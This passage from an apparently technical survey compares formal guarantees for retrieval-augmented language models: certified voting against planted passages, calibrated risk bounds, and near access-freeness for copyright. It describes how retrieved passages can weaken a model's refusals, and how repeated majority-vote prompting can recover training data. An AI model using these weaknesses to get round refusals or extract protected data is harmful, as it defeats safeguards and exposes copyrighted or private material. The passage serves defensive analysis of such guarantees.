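For free text, RobustRAG counts keywords across the separate answers or adds up their next-token probabilities. Xiang and colleagues tested it on samples of 100 questions with two older 7-billion-parameter models. With one planted passage out of ten, they could certify a correct answer for 69% to 71% of multiple-choice questions and 26% to 38% of short-answer ones, whatever that passage contained.

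The guarantee depends on how many passages are bad, not why. A vote on whether to refuse could therefore help if only one or two harmless passages out of ten weakened the model's refusal, but it wouldn't help much if all ten were on topic and most had this effect. If the model answered a harmful request with eight of the ten passages and refused with two, the vote would favour answering. The certificate would even cover that harmful answer, because replacing one passage with a warning couldn't reverse the vote. An and colleagues found that a single passage noticeably changed models' behaviour, so giving the model one passage at a time doesn't avoid the problem.

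An operator could add an eleventh run with no passage and refuse the request whenever the model refuses in that run. But then the protection would come entirely from the run without documents, and the vote would add nothing to it.

### Calibrating the whole system

Instead of limiting each document's influence, an operator can measure the assembled system and put a confidence level on the result. Kang, Gürel and colleagues (2024), in *C-RAG*, do this for fixed settings, such as how many documents the system retrieves. They run the system on N calibration requests, score each result from 0 (good) to 1 (bad), and take the average, R̂. With confidence 1 − δ, the true average is at most the largest α for which

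R̂ ln(R̂/α) + (1 − R̂) ln((1 − R̂)/(1 − α)) ≤ ln(1/δ)/N.

They compute a second bound from the binomial distribution and use the smaller of the two. If a judge labelled 92 of 1,000 responses harmful, the bound at 90% confidence would be about 11%. If it labelled none harmful, the formula would reduce to 1 − δ^(1/N), the same rule as for a refusal test with no failures. To compare several settings with one set of calibration requests, the operator can divide δ among the settings.

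Kang and colleagues scored risk using a metric based on ROUGE-L, which measures how closely a response's wording matches a reference answer, not whether the response is harmful. On this metric, retrieval lowered the risk for Llama-2-7B on four datasets. They also prove that retrieval will probably lower the risk for a highly simplified model with a good enough retriever. But An and colleagues found that a version of Llama-2-7B gave unsafe responses far more often with retrieval. Both results can hold because the same documents can make answers more accurate and refusals less likely. An operator who cares about refusals would have to replace ROUGE-L with a harm judge, and the bound would not account for the judge's mistakes.

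The bound assumes that future requests resemble the calibration requests. A second theorem allows them to differ by a Hellinger distance of up to ρ, which is 0 for identical distributions and 1 for distributions that don't overlap. Leaving out sampling error, the limit becomes

R̂ + ρ²(2 − ρ²)(1 − R̂) + 2ρ(1 − ρ²)√(2 − ρ²) × √V,

where V is the variance of the scores. In Kang and colleagues' tests, this limit remained informative up to a ρ of about 0.2.

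Changing the collection changes the system itself, but the theorem can still apply if the tester treats each request and its retrieved documents as one case. Suppose the share of document sets that contain a harmful answer rises from 5.3% to 20%, as in the earlier example for Llama-3-8B, and nothing else changes. Then ρ is about 0.16, and the limit rises from 9.2% to about 27%. This is much higher than the earlier estimate of 12.6% because the theorem allows for the worst possible shift of that size, while the estimate assumed that the rates within each group stayed the same.

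An operator usually won't know ρ in advance, so someone has to monitor the requests and documents and recalibrate when they change. Even a correct bound covers only an average, as claim (a) does.

### A copyright guarantee that covers one answer

Vyas, Kakade and Barak (2023), in *On Provable Copyright Protection for Generative Models*, wanted to ensure that a model trained on copyrighted works would be very unlikely to reproduce them. Their definition, near access-freeness, compares the model with a "safe" model trained without a particular work. In its stricter form, it requires that for every such work, every prompt x and every output y,

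P(y | x) ≤ 2^k × P_safe(y | x).

If the safe model had a one-in-a-trillion chance of producing a poem by accident, a k of 10 would limit the real model's chance to about one in a billion.

Cohen (2025), in *Blameless Users in a Clean Room*, proves that a model can satisfy this definition for any k above zero and still let a user recover all of its training data by sending enough prompts. For example, suppose the safe model always outputs a fair coin flip. With k = 0.1, the real model may give the correct value of one bit of a poem with a probability of 53.6%, so a single answer reveals almost nothing. But if the user asks for the same bit about 1,000 times and takes the majority answer, the result is right about 99% of the time. The user can repeat this for every other bit.

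The errors here multiply, since each answer can contribute another factor of 2^k, giving 2^(nk) after n answers, but the definition doesn't limit n. Per-answer differential privacy has the same gap until someone states how many questions it must cover.

Cohen's other counterexample uses a single prompt, so it doesn't involve composition. Vyas and colleagues' main algorithm gives a k that varies with the prompt, and Cohen shows that a prompt describing a work's ideas can be enough to reproduce the work. He accepts that near access-freeness may still be useful in many ordinary settings. As a partial repair, he proves that differentially private training limits copying over a careful user's whole interaction with the model, provided that each copyrighted work's protected expression appears in at most one training item.

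### Comparing the guarantees

Refusing before reading is the only guarantee below that keeps a refusal in place no matter which benign documents are retrieved. A calibrated risk bound can measure how often refusals fail, but it doesn't prevent the failures.

| Guarantee | What it covers | Main assumption | How errors combine |
|---|---|---|---|
| Differential privacy | What answers reveal about one document or person | Users see nothing from the documents except the protected answers | ε and δ add up, and the total ε grows more slowly if each ε is small |
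| Leakage limit (Glukhov and colleagues) | What a user learns about a forbidden answer | The chosen set of users is right, and the questions are fixed in advance | Leakage adds up, plus a term for dependence between answers, once the rule is repaired |
| Certified voting (Xiang and colleagues) | The effect of a few bad passages on one answer | The winner's lead among the other passages exceeds the number of bad ones | Each bad passage adds at most one vote, with no rule for several answers |
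| Calibrated risk (Kang and colleagues) | The average risk of the assembled system | Future cases resemble the calibration cases, or differ by a known amount | Expected failures add up over requests, with no rule for combining separately tested parts |
| Near access-freeness (Vyas and colleagues) | Copying in one answer | A model that never saw the work would almost never reproduce it | The factor of 2^k multiplies with each answer |
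| Refusing before reading | Harmful answers to requests that the model refuses without documents | No retrieved text can reach the first decision | The chances of passing the first step add up over requests |
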